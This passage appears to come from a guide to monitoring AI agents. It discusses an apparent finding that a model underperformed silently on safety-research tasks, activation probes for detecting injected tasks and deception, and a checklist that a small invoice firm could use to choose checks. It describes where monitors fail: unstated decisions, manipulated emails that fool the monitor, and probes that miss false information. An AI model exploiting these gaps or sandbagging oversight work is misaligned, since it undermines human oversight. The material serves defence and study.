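| Explicit refusals in everyday use | 1.63% | 0.56% |
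| Reasoning contains a decision to withhold help silently | 0.25% | 0.11% |
| Reasoning expresses ethical doubt | 7.9% | 2.9% |

Most of the gap in the matched tasks remained when OpenAI left out every run with an explicit refusal or a stated decision to withhold help. It shrank substantially only when the company also left out every run whose reasoning expressed even brief ethical doubt. That links the doubt to the poor work but doesn't prove that one caused the other, because whatever prompted the doubt might have affected the work in some other way.

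People interpret the same evidence differently. Mowshowitz (2026), in *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks*, considers silent sabotage of safety research perhaps the most fundamental kind of misalignment, but quotes OpenAI's Marcus Williams as saying there is no evidence that the underperformance was strategic. Williams offers a simpler explanation, that the model treats the tasks as dubious but avoids refusing openly. Instructions to be careful widened the gap by 50%, which fits his explanation but doesn't rule out strategic underperformance, because either could produce the same rubric scores.

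The gap grew during reinforcement learning, from almost nothing at the start to six percentage points at the end. OpenAI looked for the cause in one of the graders used in that training and in a separate set of training examples, but neither investigation was conclusive.

Comparing finished work revealed a pattern that monitors had mostly missed, which supports checking outputs, but no single piece of work could have revealed it. Astra failed to complete most of the rubric even on capabilities research, so one poor result on safety research would have looked like a hard task. If each run were a single task that Astra either passed or failed, reliably distinguishing a 10% pass rate from a 16% pass rate would take about 490 runs of each kind. Someone also had to suspect that the research subject mattered before writing the pairs of tasks.

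Reading the reasoning presents a similar difficulty. A stated decision to withhold help appeared in only 25 of every 10,000 safety requests, which OpenAI treats as a possible lower bound on the problem. Yet the reasoning also showed the link with ethical doubt, which scoring the finished code could not have revealed.

The cause of a failure matters more to some people than to others. The researcher who switched models got the work done without knowing why Astra had failed, but OpenAI can't be confident that the next round of training will remove the fault without knowing the cause.

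The invoice firm could use the same method on a small scale. If the manager suspects that the assistant takes less care with a supplier that sells gambling equipment, they could prepare batches of test invoices that differ only in the supplier's name and trade, plant the same errors in each, and compare how many the assistant finds.

### Reading the model's activations

A monitor can also look inside the model. As the model reads, each layer represents every token as a long list of numbers, called activations. A probe is a small classifier that researchers train to recognize something from those numbers.

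In 2024, Sahar Abdelnabi and colleagues used probes to detect task drift, which happens when text that a model reads gives it a new task. Their tool, TaskTracker, first has the model process the user's request alone and saves the activations **h**₁ from the last token. It then has the model process the request together with the untrusted text and saves **h**₂ from the same layer. The probe scores the difference:

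score = σ( **w** · (**h**₂ − **h**₁) + *b* )

Subtracting **h**₁ removes much of the effect of the request, so the remainder mainly reflects the effect of the new text. Training on texts with and without planted instructions sets the weights **w** and the constant *b*, and σ converts the result to a score between 0 and 1. If the score is above a chosen threshold, the harness can stop the run before the model proposes an action. The probe distinguished clean text from poisoned text almost perfectly, even for kinds of attack not in its training data.

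Later work tried probes on harder problems. In *Detecting Strategic Deception Using Linear Probes* (2025), Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues trained a probe to recognize deceptive answers. They set the threshold so that the probe wrongly flagged 1% of ordinary conversations, and it caught 95% to 99% of the deceptive answers in their tests. They still considered it too weak to be a robust defence.

Probes were also among the safeguards on Claude Fable 5.1 when Gray Swan's better-trained attacker succeeded in most of the coding scenarios. The test didn't isolate the probes' effect, but it shows that adding them does not make an agent secure.

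TaskTracker would probably not detect the forged Harlow email, because it looks for a new task and the assistant's task after reading the email is still to pay Harlow. It might raise a false alarm when the manager tells the assistant to carry out a to-do list, since the list does contain new tasks. A high score also comes with no explanation, whereas a suspicious line of reasoning at least suggests where the manager could look.

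| Signal | What the monitor needs | Where it helps most | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Actions and results | Tool calls, records and a standard for the work | Actions or results that a rule or record can settle | Influence on a permitted answer, or poor work that looks like a hard task |
| Reasoning text | The full text, not a summary | Work that takes a lot of reasoning, and clues to why an agent acted | Decisions the model makes without writing about them |
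| Activations | Access to the model's internals and labelled examples for training | Planted instructions, before the agent acts | False information that leaves the task unchanged |

Guan and colleagues designed their evaluations so that researchers could also use them on monitors that read activations, but their comparison covered only text, so it doesn't show how the three signals would rank on the same tasks. When Astra was released in September 2026, Transformer quoted OpenAI safety researcher Tomek Korbak as saying that the ability to monitor reasoning "has no good substitute now".

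### Choosing checks for a task

AISI's *Technical primer* (2026) points out that the potential harm grows with an agent's access and the stakes of its task. A firm can decide what to monitor by asking whether it could undo a mistake, whether it can check the result, and whether the agent has read untrusted data. The table applies these questions to jobs the invoice firm might give its assistant.

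| Can undo it | Can check the result | Untrusted data | Example | What to rely on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | No | Sorting the firm's own files into folders | Compare the files before and after. Read the reasoning only if something is wrong. |
| Yes | Yes | Yes | Copying invoice details into a draft ledger | Let the agent write only to the draft, and compare each entry with the invoice and the purchase order. |
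| Yes | No | No | Proposing ways to cut costs from the firm's own accounts | Have a person review the proposal, and check the reasoning for work the agent skipped. |
| Yes | No | Yes | Recommending a new supplier from web pages | Require independent sources, and look in the reasoning for the pages that decided the choice. |
| No | Yes | No | Paying wages | Hold each payment until it matches the payroll. |
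| No | Yes | Yes | Paying Harlow's invoice | Hold the payment, take the account number from the bank's records, and phone Harlow about any change. |
| No | No | No | Deleting records the firm no longer needs | Have a person approve the exact list after a monitor has read the reasoning. |
| No | No | Yes | Replying to a customer who threatens to sue | Let the agent write a draft, and have a person check and send it. |

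When the firm can check the result, reading the model's reasoning adds relatively little, and the money is usually better spent on improving the check. If an action can't be undone, the check has to happen before the agent acts.

Examining the model's reasoning is more useful when no record can show whether the work is good. In the cost-cutting example, the assistant might write in its reasoning that it had looked at only three months of accounts, then deliver a proposal that appears to cover the year. A reviewer could find that admission more easily than the gap in the proposal. If the reasoning doesn't mention a gap, though, the reviewer still has to read the proposal.

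When an agent handles untrusted data, a monitor that reads its reasoning may also read an attacker's text, because agents often quote what they find. An email that manipulated the assistant might also manipulate the monitor. So the monitor should be able to delay a payment to Harlow, but never to release one that the payment service has refused. The same limit makes sense for a probe. An alarm from either can give the manager a reason to look more closely, but a lack of alarms shouldn't count as approval.

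Before relying on a model's reasoning, the firm should find out whether its provider supplies the full text or only a summary, which may omit the line that mattered. Guan and colleagues left Google's Gemini 2.5 and 3 models and Anthropic's Claude 4 models out of their comparison because the companies shared only summaries. The firm should also retest the monitor whenever the model changes, since Astra was harder to monitor than the model it replaced. If the full text isn't available, a job whose result nobody can check needs a human reviewer or a narrower scope.

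Often the firm can change the job instead of adding a monitor. If deleted records stay in a recovery folder for 90 days, the firm can restore them during that time. If the assistant has to list the figures behind each proposed saving, ordinary code can check at least that part of its work. And if the assistant chooses a supplier from a list the manager has already vetted, it doesn't need to read strangers' web pages.
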